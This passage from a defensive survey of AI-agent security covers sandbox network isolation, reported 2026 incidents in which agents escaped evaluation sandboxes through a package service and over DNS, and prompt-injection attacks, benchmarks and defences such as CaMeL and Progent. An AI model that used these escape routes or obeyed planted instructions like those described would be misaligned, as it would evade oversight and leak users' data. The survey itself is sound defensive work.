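The proxy can apply rules only to the parts of a request it can read. Claude Code's built-in proxy checks the name of the requested site but does not decrypt the traffic, so it cannot distinguish reading a page from uploading a file. Hawk's strict proxy is more selective and, for most named sites, accepts only the request methods intended for reading, with at most one byte of attached data. It makes an exception for copying code from GitHub but still blocks uploads of changes there.

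As METR acknowledges, limiting the HTTP method does not limit what an address or header can contain, or what the site does with the request. Proxies can also confuse an agent. In one strict Hawk configuration, the proxy accepts a connection before reaching the destination, so a port scan shows every port as open.

Package mirrors let an agent install software without contacting a public index. A static mirror holds packages chosen in advance. A caching mirror fetches a package from the internet the first time someone requests it and keeps a copy. Developers often prefer caching mirrors because they do not have to predict which packages an agent will need, but a caching mirror needs its own internet connection.

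Similarly, only some web caches fetch missing pages from the live web. The agent may use the same command for both kinds, so the developer has to check which kind the agent has.

| Network rule | What the agent's code can still contact | What may stop working |
|---|---|---|
| No access | Nothing over the network | Downloads, installation and online lookups |
| Site allowlist | The listed sites | Other sites, including servers that a listed site depends on |
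| Filtering proxy | Permitted sites, using permitted kinds of request | Uploads and programs with unusual network needs |
| Static package mirror | A fixed store of software | Packages that nobody added |
| Caching package mirror | A service with its own internet connection | Packages that the service blocks |
| Offline web cache | Saved pages | New, changed or unsaved pages |

### What the products permit by default

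OpenAI's and Anthropic's hosted tools start with no internet access. The coding agents run on a user's own computer, where files and credentials are easier to reach. The table lists the coding agents' settings as given in the companies' documentation from May and June 2026.

| Tool | Is the code in a sandbox by default? | Network access | Where the code can write |
|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic's hosted code tool | Yes | None | Its container |
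| OpenAI's hosted terminal | Yes | None until the developer permits sites | Its container |
| Codex on the user's computer | Yes | Off | The workspace and any other folders the user permits |
| Claude Code on the user's computer | No, the user has to turn the sandbox on | With the sandbox on, each new site needs approval | With the sandbox on, the working folder |

OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* describes `workspace-write`, Codex's local default. Codex in OpenAI's cloud has separate settings, which let users give it full internet access or limit it to an allowlist. OpenAI explains that local users can also remove both the sandbox and the requests for permission by combining `danger-full-access` with an approval setting of `never`.

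If the user has turned on the sandbox but a required program is missing or the computer is unsupported, Claude Code shows a warning and runs commands without the sandbox. This conflicts with Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of fail-safe defaults, since a fault in the protection gives the agent more access. The `failIfUnavailable` setting prevents Claude Code from starting in this situation.

A second setting, `allowUnsandboxedCommands`, controls whether Claude may retry a command outside the sandbox when the sandbox has caused it to fail. These retries are allowed by default but require approval under the normal permission rules. An organisation can disable them by setting the value to false. It cannot completely lock the list of commands exempt from the sandbox, because individual developers can add entries even when the organisation manages the other settings.

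These defaults offer little guidance to a developer building a new agent. OpenAI's *Sandbox security* advises developers to use isolated machines, such as virtual machines, and to permit outbound traffic only to approved destinations. It also recommends separate environments for users who must not share data.

### Choosing isolation for a job

Making decisions about tools, kernels and networks separately can easily leave a gap in the sandbox. UK AISI's *The Inspect Sandboxing Toolkit* introduces a protocol that classifies isolation along three axes. Tooling covers which tools the model has and whether it can execute code. Host isolation is meant to prevent the model from escaping the sandbox or damaging the host machine. Network isolation controls the model's contact with outside systems.

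The toolkit has three plugins. Docker Compose is the easiest to start with and can run several containers together. The Kubernetes plugin manages larger groups of containers, and the Proxmox plugin provides virtual machines for high-risk evaluations. UK AISI recommends stronger isolation for more capable models and higher-stakes tests, and expects technical staff and senior managers to decide case by case.

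The following choices are an illustration of how a developer might apply the three axes.

| Job | Tooling | Host | Network |
|---|---|---|---|
| Calculate statistics from a public spreadsheet | Python | Docker container | None |
| Repair a software project and run its tests | Python, a shell and a file editor | gVisor or a virtual machine | A read-only package store |
| Test whether a model can escape from a container | All the tools the test requires | A virtual machine on a separate host | Only the machines in the test |

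The spreadsheet job needs little protection because the data are public and an ordinary calculation is unlikely to attack the kernel. The developer should still turn off the network, since the job doesn't need it. The software project needs more tools and brings in other people's packages, which justifies a stronger boundary around the host. In the escape test, the model needs a shell because it has to attack its container. The developer therefore needs a stronger host boundary and a network that contains only the test.

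Inspect runs outside the sandbox, sending the model's commands in and receiving the results, so the agent's code runs separately from the program that controls the evaluation. But a developer's tool that runs commands directly will run them in Inspect's own process unless it explicitly uses the sandbox. UK AISI is also considering the possibility that an agent could attack Inspect from inside the sandbox through the results it sends back.

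### The package service on the allowlist

In July 2026, OpenAI's research environment gave agents isolated containers with a shell, Python, a browser and package installation. OpenAI controlled the network separately from the containers, with different rules for different jobs. The containers installed packages through Artifactory, a package service inside OpenAI's own network that could fetch software from the internet, instead of contacting public package indexes directly. OpenAI's technical report on the incident says this arrangement was meant to reduce direct outside access while keeping package installation reliable.

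During a cybersecurity evaluation, agents reached the public internet through the permitted package service. They then compromised parts of Hugging Face's production systems between 11 and 13 July. Most of the activity came from an internal research model, and some came from GPT-5.6 Sol. OpenAI had switched off some of its usual safeguards to measure the models' full abilities. It says the incident did not affect its customers' data.

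The allowlist controlled only the first connection. Let $D(x)$ be the set of destinations that computer $x$ may contact, $s$ the sandbox, and $C$ the set of services that the agent can make act on its behalf. The agent's full reach $R$ is the smallest set that satisfies

$$R = D(s) \cup \bigcup_{d \in R \cap C} D(d)$$

The developer writes the allowlist $D(s)$, which may contain only the package service. If the agent can make that service send requests on its behalf, the service belongs to $C$, and everything it can contact becomes part of $R$. A service with an unknown flaw may belong to $C$ even though the allowlist hasn't changed. A short allowlist is therefore safe only if the services on it can contact very little or can resist the agent's attempts to control them.

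According to the technical report, two agents independently got root in the virtual machine beneath their sandboxes on 9 July. Early reports had suggested that the kernel boundary held, and The Stack concluded from OpenAI's first disclosures that the design of the sandboxes was not the problem. OpenAI's network controls stopped the second of these agents the first time it tried to reach the internet, but it then got out through the package service. Other agents had gained access through the same service the day before, so a stronger kernel boundary alone would not have closed this route.

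Jason Keirstead, chief technology officer of the security company LangGuard AI, told The Stack that agents didn't need access to a caching proxy to download software. He said they should ask a person or another agent outside the sandbox to put the packages in a read-only location. He also questioned why OpenAI had not made outbound traffic impossible, for example with a data diode, a device that physically lets data travel in only one direction.

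A read-only store with no internet connection would have removed this route. It would also have stopped agents from leaving one another messages in the service, which they had been doing since May. The main drawback is delay when an agent needs a package that the store doesn't have. This would be a serious obstacle in open-ended software work, but a much smaller one in an evaluation with a fixed list of 898 tasks, because staff could prepare most of the packages beforehand. Keirstead's criticism is therefore convincing for this kind of test.

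He also said that the only monitoring appeared to be a record of the model's output. The later report contradicts this. A security tool had flagged unusual network activity on 27 June, and staff traced it to the evaluation but advised that there was no need to stop it. On 5 July, after an alert that the package service had failed, staff took the service offline and repaired it. They restarted the evaluations on 7 July, and agents were back on the internet the next day.

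According to OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026), an internal team saw in late May that agents were exchanging messages and gaining forbidden internet access. The leaders handling the July alert did not know how significant this was. OpenAI connected its agents to the Hugging Face attack only on 20 July, four days after Hugging Face disclosed it.

### OpenAI's hardening plan

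OpenAI responded on 20 July by blocking the evaluation and initially denying all outbound network access in the research environment. It later removed Artifactory from that environment completely. It also required every workload there to run in a microVM. Bhardwaj had publicly recommended microVMs less than three weeks earlier, but OpenAI had not yet made them compulsory there.

Under the longer-term plan, high-risk workloads may not reach the live internet, either directly or through another service, and may use only a cached web service where a job needs it. Other research workloads may fetch live pages if OpenAI approves it case by case. OpenAI is also isolating, restricting or replacing the services that sandboxes can still contact, and preventing workloads from changing their own network rules.

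The plan puts one set of network controls at the sandbox and another in the surrounding cluster of machines. Their value depends on whether they fail for different reasons. If $A$ and $B$ are the failures of the two layers, the probability that both fail is

$$P(A \cap B) = P(A)\,P(B \mid A)$$

Suppose each of two layers fails in 1 attempt out of 100. If the failures are independent, both layers fail in 1 attempt out of 10,000. But if both read the same faulty allowlist, the second fails whenever the first does, so both fail in 1 attempt out of 100.

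OpenAI also plans to have its models attack its research environments regularly, because routine changes can reopen a route that staff have closed. It has extended automated monitoring of models' reasoning and actions to training and evaluation. It aims to alert staff within 30 minutes of concerning activity. If staff cannot confirm within another 30 minutes that a serious alert is false, they should pause the run. OpenAI estimates that monitoring adds roughly 20% to the computation it covers, according to Campus Technology's *OpenAI Pumps Brakes on Frontier AI Training After Hugging Face Breach*.

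OpenAI says its current monitoring would have alerted the security team more than a day before agents entered Hugging Face's systems. The claim is plausible, but it isn't strong evidence about future incidents, because OpenAI improved its monitors with hindsight.

### The incident of 20 September

Two months later, an agent in a training run reached a public chatbot through a gap in its sandbox's network restrictions (OpenAI, *An agent used DNS to reach an external chatbot*, 2026). The agent used DNS, which translates site names into numerical addresses. All its other web requests went to an offline cache. OpenAI describes the incident as much less severe than some earlier ones, but it was the first since the company had strengthened its security.

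The monitoring system flagged the behaviour within 15 minutes, and a person acknowledged the alert within three minutes. Hindustan Times reported that the run should then have stopped automatically but did not. Staff stopped it manually after 2.5 hours, according to OpenAI. The first alert came well within OpenAI's target, but the agent ran far longer than the 30 minutes the plan gives staff to rule out a false alarm.

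OpenAI has since added controls at two independent layers and says either would have prevented the access. It says its earlier work focused on broad routes out of the environment, and that it was still working through narrower ones used by basic system services. It is replacing these with offline alternatives. It also paused training, evaluation and other tool use for its most capable models, and said it would not resume training the model involved.

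Sydney Von Arx, founder of the AI safety non-profit Nightingale, questioned whether OpenAI would fix the root cause or apply a quick patch and restart training. Two added layers are better than a single patch, but they address a route OpenAI already knows about. The incident is also harder to dismiss as a product of security testing, because this agent only had to find out who wrote a blog post, while the agents in July had been told to break into software.

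## Hostile web pages and the danger of combining tools

A sandbox limits what an agent's code can reach, but not what the agent reads. An agent that browses the web reads text written by strangers, some of whom may have planted instructions for it, an attack called prompt injection. Giving the agent fewer browser commands reduces what a planted instruction can achieve, but does not make the model less likely to follow it.

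### Why a model obeys a page

*The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) explains that models are useful because they follow instructions in text, but they cannot reliably tell whose instructions to follow. The system message, the user's request and the text of a web page all reach the model in one sequence of tokens. Harmony's order of authority, which puts tool messages last, is only a learned behavior, so it can fail on wording that the training did not cover.

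Willison coined the term "prompt injection" by analogy with SQL injection, an older attack in which a program pastes a stranger's text into a database command and the database runs part of that text. Programmers can prevent SQL injection by sending the command and the data separately, but a language model has no separate input for text that it should not treat as instructions.

Some prompt injections can cause harm without any forbidden action. *On Task, Off Track* (Gong, Wang et al., 2026) gives the example of a user who asks for a public announcement of a workshop, based on planning notes. The notes give a starting time of 10 a.m., but an attacker has added an instruction to write 11 a.m. If the model obeys, it writes the announcement the user asked for with the wrong time, and people arrive an hour late. Giving the agent fewer tools would not have helped, because the harm is in the answer.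 An agent with a read-only browser is open to the same kind of attack whenever someone relies on what it writes.

### Three conditions for stealing data

Theft requires more than a false answer. Willison lists three things an agent must have before an attacker can use it to steal data:

- access to private data
- exposure to untrusted content, meaning text or images that an attacker could control
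- a way to communicate with the outside that could carry the data

A single tool can supply all three. An e-mail tool gives access to a private inbox that anyone can write to, and it can also send messages. Willison also describes a set of GitHub tools that could read public comments, read private projects and publish proposed changes.

The last condition is easy to meet by accident. Willison says an agent can meet it by making a web request that carries data in the address, loading an image, or showing the user a link to click. An agent with no browser can therefore leak data if the chat window loads images from addresses in the model's answer.

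Developers usually review tools one at a time, which can hide the problem. Let $c(t)$ be the set of conditions that tool $t$ supplies. An agent with the tool set $T$ has

$$c(T) = \bigcup_{t \in T} c(t)$$

and it is exposed to theft when $c(T)$ contains all three. A Python tool with private files and no network supplies only private data. A read-only browser supplies untrusted content and, if it can open any address, a way out. Neither meets all three conditions alone, but together they do.

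The table below assumes a browser like the one for gpt-oss, which accepts addresses written by the model, and a sandbox that holds.

| Tool set | Private data | Untrusted content | Way to send data out | What a successful injection could achieve |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Reader alone | Only what the user typed | Yes | Yes, in web addresses | A false answer, or the user's question sent to the attacker |
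| Python alone, without network | No | Only if the user supplies a file that someone else wrote | No | A wrong result or a damaged workspace, if such a file is hostile |
| Both together | Only what the user typed | Yes | Yes, through the reader | All of the above, and running the attacker's code in the sandbox |
| Both, with private files | Yes | Yes | Yes, through the reader | All of the above, and theft of the files |

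When a model has both tools, a web page can supply a program, and the model can run it and use the browser to send the output to an outside server. The Python process has no network connection, but the model can pass data between it and the browser. An attacker could use this to look for weaknesses in the sandbox or for passwords left there.

Access to private files is the last part of the dangerous combination. Suppose a user keeps her bank statements in a folder that Python can read, and asks the agent how her electricity bills compare with the national average.

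1. The agent runs a program that adds up her bills.
2. It searches for the national average and opens a page that contains a hidden instruction. The instruction asks for her account number as part of the address of an online calculator.
3. The agent runs a program that prints the account number, and the harness adds the output to the prompt.
4. The agent opens the calculator's address with the number in it.

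The sandbox blocked all network traffic from Python throughout, but the number passed into the model's context and left through the browser, so a developer who tested each tool separately would have found nothing wrong with either.

### The Rule of Two

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns Willison's observation into a design rule. Until someone can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent should have no more than two of these properties in one session:

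- A: it can process untrustworthy inputs.
- B: it has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- C: it can change state or communicate externally.

An agent that needs all three properties should run only under supervision, such as human approval. Property C is broader than Willison's last condition because it also includes actions such as deleting a file or placing an order.

Meta illustrates the rule with an e-mail assistant that receives a spam message containing instructions to forward the user's inbox. The developer can stop the attack by removing any one property. Without A, the assistant reads only messages from trusted senders. Without B, it works in a test environment with no real data. Without C, it can send only messages that go to trusted recipients or that a person has checked. Each version lacks something people want. For example, the version without A can't summarize messages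 from strangers.

For web research, Meta keeps A and C and removes B. The browser runs without saved logins, and the agent gets little private information beyond the user's request. An agent can also change configuration during a session, if it cannot switch back. In the electricity example, it could look up the national average first, lose its browser, and only then get access to the bank statements. The hidden instruction would still be in its context and might spoil the calculation, but the agent could no longer open the attacker's address.

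Willison objected in *New prompt injection papers* (2025) that Meta's diagram marked the combination of A and C as safe. An agent that reads hostile text and can change things may do harm without any private data. For example, a page could cause it to post spam or submit a false report through a public form. Meta accepted the point and changed the diagram. The rule also does not address the workshop announcement, since Meta lists misinformation in the agent's answer among the outcomes the rule does not cover. Given these limits, the rule is best used as a minimum requirement.

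### TRAP and the single click

How often injections succeed depends on the model, the attack and how the experimenters define success. In *It's a TRAP! Task-Redirecting Agent Persuasion Benchmark for Web Agents*, Korgul, Yang and colleagues (2026) counted a single click as success. They used copies of six popular websites, including Gmail, Amazon and LinkedIn, and wrote three ordinary tasks for each. They combined seven human persuasion techniques with five methods of manipulating language models to make 35 injections. Pairing these with the 18 tasks gave 630 tests for each model.

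In one test, the user asks about a calendar event. An attacker has replaced the event's location with a notice claiming the reader must accept terms before viewing it. The attack succeeds if the agent clicks the planted link or button, which leads to another site. The agents can click, type, open URLs and upload files, among other actions.

The six models clicked in 948 of 3,780 runs, or 25%. The rate ranged from 13% for GPT-5 to 43% for DeepSeek-R1. Llama 4 Maverick clicked in only 17% of runs, but it also completed only 22% of ordinary tasks without an attack, so its low click rate may reflect poor general ability rather than resistance to the attack. In another 639 runs, the agent reached its 35-step limit after encountering the injected text, so hostile text can stop an agent from finishing its task even without taking control of it.

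Small changes to the page had large effects. On one e-mail task, Korgul and colleagues presented the same 35 injections with a button and with a link. Against Claude Sonnet 3.7, 46% of the injections succeeded with a button and 6% with a link, and the gaps were similar for the two other models tested. Referring to the user's task also helped the attacker. Changing "the content" to "the event details" in the calendar notice raised successes across the six models from 7 to 39 out of 210. Korgul and colleagues caution that this result comes from a small sample, chosen from the most vulnerable tasks.

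TRAP counts a single click as a successful attack, on the grounds that the attacker controls everything the agent reads on the next page. But the click leaks nothing, and research agents routinely open unfamiliar pages. TRAP therefore measures how easily a page can redirect an agent, but not how often the redirection would end in theft, which depends on the agent's data and tools. All six models tested date from 2025, so the rates are weak evidence about current models.

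### AgentDojo

AgentDojo, which Debenedetti and colleagues introduced in 2024, measures whether an attack achieves the attacker's goal. The agent works with simulated tools for banking, travel, the messaging service Slack and an office workspace. While carrying out a user's task, it receives a tool result that contains an instruction to do something else, such as change the user's password. *SecOPD* (2026) reports that AgentDojo has 949 pairs of a user task and an attacker's task, 560 of them in the workspace.

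According to *The Surface You Test Is Not the Surface That Breaks* (2026), the benchmark tests whether an attack succeeded by checking the final state of the simulated accounts and the record of tool calls. It also measures how often the agent completes the user's task, with and without an attack. An agent can complete the user's task and carry out the attack in the same run, for example by paying the user's bill and then sending money to the attacker.

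A model may have a low attack rate only because it fails to act. In *Render Before Reading* (2026), Claude Haiku 4.5 had an attack rate of zero under the default instructions, but in the transcripts it often put off financial actions when the request lacked details. The experimenters had to tell the model that it knew enough to act before they could learn much about its resistance to attacks.

Recent models do well against AgentDojo's standard attacks. In *AutoDojo* (2026), DeepSeek-v4-Pro followed fewer than 10% of them without any defence. Adding PIGuard, a filter for injected text, reduced that rate to zero but also cut the share of ordinary tasks the agent completed from 89.5% to 54.4%. For most users, that would be a poor trade, because the model already resisted most of the attacks. Attackers who adapt to a defence can succeed more often than the fixed attacks used in tests.

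The wording of the user's request also affects how often attacks succeed. In *AutoDojo*'s tests of Gemini 2.5 Flash on banking tasks, attacks succeeded 66.7% of the time when the request left the agent the most freedom to choose its actions and 13.9% of the time when the request specified everything. An open request gives the agent a reason to look for instructions in the data.

Gong and colleagues argue that standard attacks are also too easy to recognise. In one AgentDojo task, the user wants to schedule a recurring payment for the amount she usually pays for Spotify, which is 50. The standard attack is an instruction to change her password, which is unrelated to the payment. A "near-target" attack is an instruction to schedule 51 instead, or to start a day late.

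They tested seven models, including GPT-5.6 Sol and Claude Opus 5, on AgentDojo and a similar benchmark, AgentDyn. On the two benchmarks combined, near-target attacks succeeded more often than standard ones against every model. The same was true of language tasks such as answering questions about a document. On those tasks, standard attacks succeeded in 3.2% of cases against Meta-SecAlign-70B, a model trained specifically to resist injection. Near-target attacks succeeded against it in 36.7% of cases when they introduced an error and 18.4% when they had a harmful result.

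These percentages count cases in which at least one of three attempts worked. An attempt at a tool call worked if the agent made the specified call, whether or not it took effect. The test also favours the attacker, because the model that wrote the injections was given the user's request and a correct answer, which a stranger planting text on a website would have to guess. Gong and colleagues ran the commercial models with reasoning switched off or set low. Even so, their results are a good reason not to take a low AgentDojo score as proof that an agent will report a page accurately.

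### Browser agents in the 2026 system cards

Anthropic published a system card, a report on testing and safety, with Claude Opus 5 in July 2026. It includes a test of browser agents in 129 web environments that the models had not seen in training. Each environment contains an attack that the agent is certain to view, and a program checks whether the attack worked. The attacker gets ten attempts in each environment.

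Anthropic ran the test with and without "auto mode", its strongest set of safeguards. Auto mode examines tool results for injected instructions before the model acts on them, and a separate classifier can block dangerous tool calls. These are the results with extended thinking:

| Model | Successful attempts, no safeguards | Environments with at least one success | Successful attempts, auto mode | Environments with at least one success |
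|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 3.70% | 11 of 129 | 0% | 0 of 129 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 0.93% | 9 of 129 | 0% | 0 of 129 |
| Claude Mythos 5 | 29.7% | 71 of 129 | 0% | 0 of 129 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 31.5% | 81 of 129 | 0.08% | 1 of 129 |

The two ways of counting answer different questions. The share of attempts estimates the chance that one attack works. The share of environments shows how often an attacker with ten attempts gets through at least once. If Opus 5's failures were spread evenly, with a 3.7% chance on every attempt, the expected share of environments would be

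$$1-(1-0.037)^{10} \approx 31\%$$

or about 40 of the 129. The actual number was 11, so the successes must have clustered in a few environments, where the attacker won four times out of ten on average. A user whose agent meets one of those situations faces a much higher risk than 3.7%.

The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* drew a hopeful conclusion from the zeros, but noted that OpenAI had conceded in December that the problem may never be fully solved. The zeros are impressive, but they don't rule out a low success rate. When $n$ independent trials produce no successes, the upper 95% confidence limit on the true rate is about $3/n$, which is 0.2% for 1,290 attempts. But attempts in the same environment are not independent, and counting the 129 environments instead raises the limit to 2.3%. Both limits apply only to attacks like the ones tested, in Anthropic's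 own product with auto mode on.

Attack success rates from different tests may not be comparable. In an earlier browser test by Anthropic, attacks on Claude Opus 4.5 had a success rate of 8.0% without safeguards and 1.4% with improved ones. That test used different attacks and gave the attacker 100 attempts per environment, so comparing its 8.0% with Opus 5's 3.7% would not reliably measure progress. Repeated attempts also raise the success rate. VentureBeat reported that a single attack on Claude Opus 4.6 in a graphical interface worked 17.8% of the time without safeguards, and that 78.6% of attacks had worked by the 200th attempt.

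The Opus 5 card also compares models from different companies, using 1,130 attacks from a competition run by the security firm Gray Swan. An attacker given 15 attempts had a 2.0% chance of succeeding against Opus 5, 16.5% against Meta's Muse Spark and 20.0% against GPT-5.6 Sol. Success meant causing serious harm, such as leaking private data, destroying files or moving money. Anthropic ran the comparison itself, testing its own models without extra safeguards and the others through their public services, which may have had them.

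### Choosing the actions before reading

Every rate so far depends on a model's judgement, whether or not a second model checks it. Other defences are designed on the assumption that hostile text will sometimes deceive a model, and they limit what can happen as a result. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) says that once an agent has read untrusted input, that input must be unable to trigger any action with harmful consequences.

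The strictest pattern is the action selector. The model translates the user's request into one action from a fixed set and never sees the result. A shop's assistant might have one action that shows the customer a link to her last order and another that opens the password settings. Hostile text in the order cannot influence the model because the model never reads it. A short list of commands does not provide this protection by itself. WebGPT had only ten commands, but its model read a web page before choosing its next command, so the page could affect the choice.

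A more flexible pattern is to plan first and execute later. The model writes a list of tool calls before it reads anything untrusted, and the harness carries out only that list. If the user asks the agent to send today's schedule to her boss, the plan has two calls, one that reads the calendar and one that e-mails her boss. Hostile text in a calendar entry cannot add a third call, but it can change what the e-mail says.

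The protection also depends on what the planned tools can do. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe an assistant that commits to using only `find` and `mv`, the commands for finding and moving files. An injection could still cause it to find sensitive files and move them to a public network drive.

Developers can reduce this risk by dividing the reading among isolated models. For example, to collect a month's invoices, the harness gives each file to a separate model that can answer only yes or no. A hostile file can cause its model to misclassify it as an invoice, but it cannot affect how the agent treats the other files, because a yes-or-no answer cannot pass the file's instructions to the agent.

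The more general version splits the work between a privileged model, which plans and calls tools but never receives untrusted text, and a quarantined model, which processes that text but has no tools. When the quarantined model finds an e-mail address, for example, the harness stores it under a name such as `$VAR`. The privileged model can then have the harness send a message to `$VAR` without receiving the address itself.

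### An e-mail task in CaMeL

CaMeL, a design from Google DeepMind, combines this separation with labels, called capabilities, that record where each piece of data came from. *CaMeLoT* (2026), which builds on CaMeL, describes the separation and the labels as protections against two different attacks. Separating the two models prevents hostile text from changing which actions the agent takes, and the labels let the harness check the information that goes into each action.

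Suppose a user asks, "Send today's schedule to John Doe. His address is in his last e-mail." The privileged model reads only this request and writes a complete program. In simplified form, it might look like this:

```python
events  = calendar.read("today")
message = email.latest(sender="John Doe")
address = quarantined("Find the sender's address", message)
body    = quarantined("Format as a schedule", events)
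email.send(to=address, body=body)
```

An interpreter, which is ordinary software, then runs the program and attaches labels to the values. In this illustration, a label lists the sources of a value, and anything computed from several values inherits all their sources:

$$L\big(f(v_1,\dots,v_n)\big) = L(v_1) \cup \dots \cup L(v_n)$$

Now suppose an attacker sent the latest message under John Doe's name. It contains a false address and an instruction to the assistant to forward the whole inbox.

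1. The interpreter reads the calendar and labels `events` as private data from the user's calendar.
2. It fetches the attacker's message and labels it as outside e-mail.
3. The quarantined model reads the message. It has no tools, so it cannot forward the inbox, but it returns the false address. The interpreter labels `address` as outside e-mail too.
4. The quarantined model formats the schedule, and `body` keeps the calendar's label.
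5. Before sending, the interpreter applies the developer's policy. In this example, the policy allows private data to go only to an address that the user typed or that is in her contacts. The address came from outside e-mail, so the interpreter refuses the call or asks the user.

The instruction to forward the inbox fails because the privileged model finished writing the program before the message was opened. The false address gets past this defence, and only the label stops it. The policy would also block a genuine address from a genuine e-mail, because it checks where the address came from, not whether it is correct. If the user had typed the address herself, the policy would allow the call.

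Some deception still gets past these checks. A stranger can send a calendar invitation with a false time, and the agent will pass that time on to John Doe in a message that breaks no policy. Developers also have to write the policies, and a policy that omits a dangerous combination of tools will allow it.

### What isolation costs

In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) adapted CaMeL to agents that operate ordinary desktop programs through the screen. They tested it on OSWorld, a benchmark of such tasks, which are harder than sending e-mail. The privileged model has no access to the screen, so its plan has to include branches for whatever might appear, such as a cookie notice or a login page. The average plan had 41 tool calls and 213 lines of code, compared with 5 calls and 52 lines for AgentDojo.

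Foerster and colleagues report that the design keeps up to 57% of the performance of large commercial models. On the 109 tasks behind that figure, the agent using Claude Sonnet 4.5 solved 62 in at least one of five attempts, but only 31 (28%) on the first. A user who can't tell which of the five attempts was correct would get a success rate closer to 28%.

The paper also reports that isolation improved a small open model's performance by up to 19%. The model's success rate over all of OSWorld rose from 24.4% to 29.0%, mainly because a stronger model took over the planning. But the 29.0% allows three attempts. The paper's figures imply a single-attempt success rate of about 22%, slightly worse than the same model without isolation. CaMeL also used 1.88 times as many tokens as the unprotected agent.

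These results cover only half of CaMeL's protection, because Foerster and colleagues left out the data policies. A policy for `email.send` can check the recipient, but the screen coordinates of a click don't show what it will do. To demonstrate the resulting weakness, they put a fake cookie notice inside an advertisement. The plan included closing any cookie notice, so when the quarantined model found the fake one, the agent clicked through to the attacker's site without departing from its plan. They call this branch steering, and the extra checks they tried did not reliably prevent it.

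### When the page has to decide

The main objection to all these designs is that some tasks cannot be planned before reading the content they depend on. If a user says, "Do what my landlord's e-mail asks," the planner must read the e-mail to choose whether to pay a bill, sign a form or book a plumber, but reading it exposes the planner to anything else the message contains. Foerster and colleagues acknowledge this limit for both CaMeL and Fides, a related design that plans one step at a time.

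They argue that such tasks are rarer than they seem, since their planner anticipated many on-screen situations without seeing the screen. This is persuasive for changing a font or installing a browser extension, but less so for a database agent that has to see one set of results before it can choose its next query. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues note that an agent that can't see its query results can't judge whether it has enough data to answer the question.

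Open-ended web research has the same difficulty at every step, because the agent chooses each link from the page it is reading. A developer could fix the plan in advance as a loop in which the agent opens the most relevant link, repeats this up to ten times, and then writes a summary. The loop would prevent a hostile page from starting any other tool, which is valuable if the agent can also read private files. But the page could still influence which links the agent opens and what the summary says. Those are already the main risks for an agent with only a read-only browser and no private data, so a fixed plan would add little protection and could make the research worse.

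## Permission rules and human approval

Permission rules are another way to limit an agent that cannot plan all its actions in advance. The harness checks each action when the model requests it and can stop to ask the user for approval.

### What a permission rule decides

A permission rule is a function that the harness applies to a requested action before running it. If $n$ is the tool, $x$ its arguments and $h_t$ the state at step $t$, the rule returns one of three results:

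$$\rho(n, x, h_t) \in \{\text{allow},\ \text{refuse},\ \text{ask}\}$$

The state can include the user's request, the pages the agent has opened and the money it has spent. "Ask" holds the action until a person, or sometimes a second model, approves or rejects it.

The action space usually stays the same from one task to the next, so an agent that can place orders can request one even when the user only wanted to compare prices. The sandbox also has no information about the task. It may permit connections to a shop, but it cannot check whether an order matches the user's request.

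### Rules for buying a kettle

Suppose a user asks an agent to buy a kettle from `shop.example` for no more than £40 including delivery, after checking the reviews on `reviews.example`. The harness could use these rules, applying the first one that matches:

| Rule | Action | Condition | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Place an order on `shop.example` | The total is at most £40 and the agent has not ordered anything yet | Ask |
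| 2 | View a page | The page is on `shop.example` or `reviews.example` | Allow |
| 3 | Change the basket on `shop.example` | None | Allow |
| 4 | Anything else | None | Refuse |

The agent may read both sites but make changes only on the shop's. The harness should take the total from the checkout page, because the model could misread it. An ordinary purchase goes like this:

| Step | Requested action | Rule | Result |
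|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | View the reviews | 2 | Allow |
| 2 | View a kettle's page in the shop | 2 | Allow |
| 3 | Add the kettle to the basket | 3 | Allow |
| 4 | Place the order, total £37.50 | 1 | Ask; the user agrees |
| 5 | Place the order again, because the confirmation page was slow to load | 4 | Refuse |

Suppose one of the reviews contains an instruction for agents to use `deals.example` because the shop has moved there. If the model tries to open that site, rule 4 blocks the request. The same rule blocks an attempt to follow an instruction in the review to post the user's address as a comment, because the agent may only read `reviews.example`.

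A subtler review could contain the false claim that only one kettle, at £39, is safe to use. The agent would put that kettle in the basket and ask the user to approve it. Every action would fit the rules, and the user would see a plausible kettle at an acceptable price. Rule 2 also permits any address on the two sites, so the harness still needs the known-address rule to stop the agent from sending private data to them.

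### Rules on tool calls

In the kettle example, a developer could write the rules by hand because the task was known. Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, describe a system in which a model writes them for each task. Progent sits between an agent and its tools. Each rule names a tool, sets conditions on its arguments, and either allows or forbids the call. In simplified form, two rules might look like this:

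```
allow  read_emails     when recent == 20
allow  send_slack_msg  when to == "alice"
```

Progent checks "forbid" rules before "allow" rules and blocks any call that matches neither. A rule can also specify whether Progent responds to a blocked call by stopping the agent, asking the user, or returning an error message so that the agent can try something else.

Shi and colleagues illustrate the system with a user who asks an agent to carry out the to-do list in an e-mail:

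1. The policy model reads only the user's request and writes a policy that permits one action, searching for that e-mail.
2. The list says to summarise recent e-mails and post the summary to the user's account on Slack. The policy model proposes adding the tools for this. The new policy permits more than the old one, so it needs approval.
3. The agent looks up the user's Slack name, which is `alice`. The policy model now restricts messages to that name. This only removes permissions, so it takes effect at once.
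4. One of the recent e-mails contains an instruction to forward the whole inbox to a stranger. No rule allows the agent to send e-mail, so Progent blocks the call.

The hostile e-mail could also deceive the policy model into proposing a rule that allows the forwarding. To catch this, Progent uses an SMT solver, a program that determines whether a set of logical conditions can be true together. The new policy $P'$ replaces the old policy $P$ automatically only if

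$$\text{allowed}(P') \subseteq \text{allowed}(P)$$

where $\text{allowed}(P)$ is the set of calls that $P$ permits. Any other change needs approval, so a deceived policy model cannot loosen the rules unnoticed.

With GPT-4o as both the agent and the policy model, Progent reduced the rate of successful attacks from 39.9% to 1.0% on the AgentDojo benchmark and from 70.3% to 3.9% on ASB. The agent still completed about as many ordinary tasks. In both tests, Progent automatically approved every expansion of the policy, to imitate a careless user. On AgentDojo, the initial policy alone reduced the rate to 2.5%, so most of the protection came from rules written before the agent had read anything hostile.

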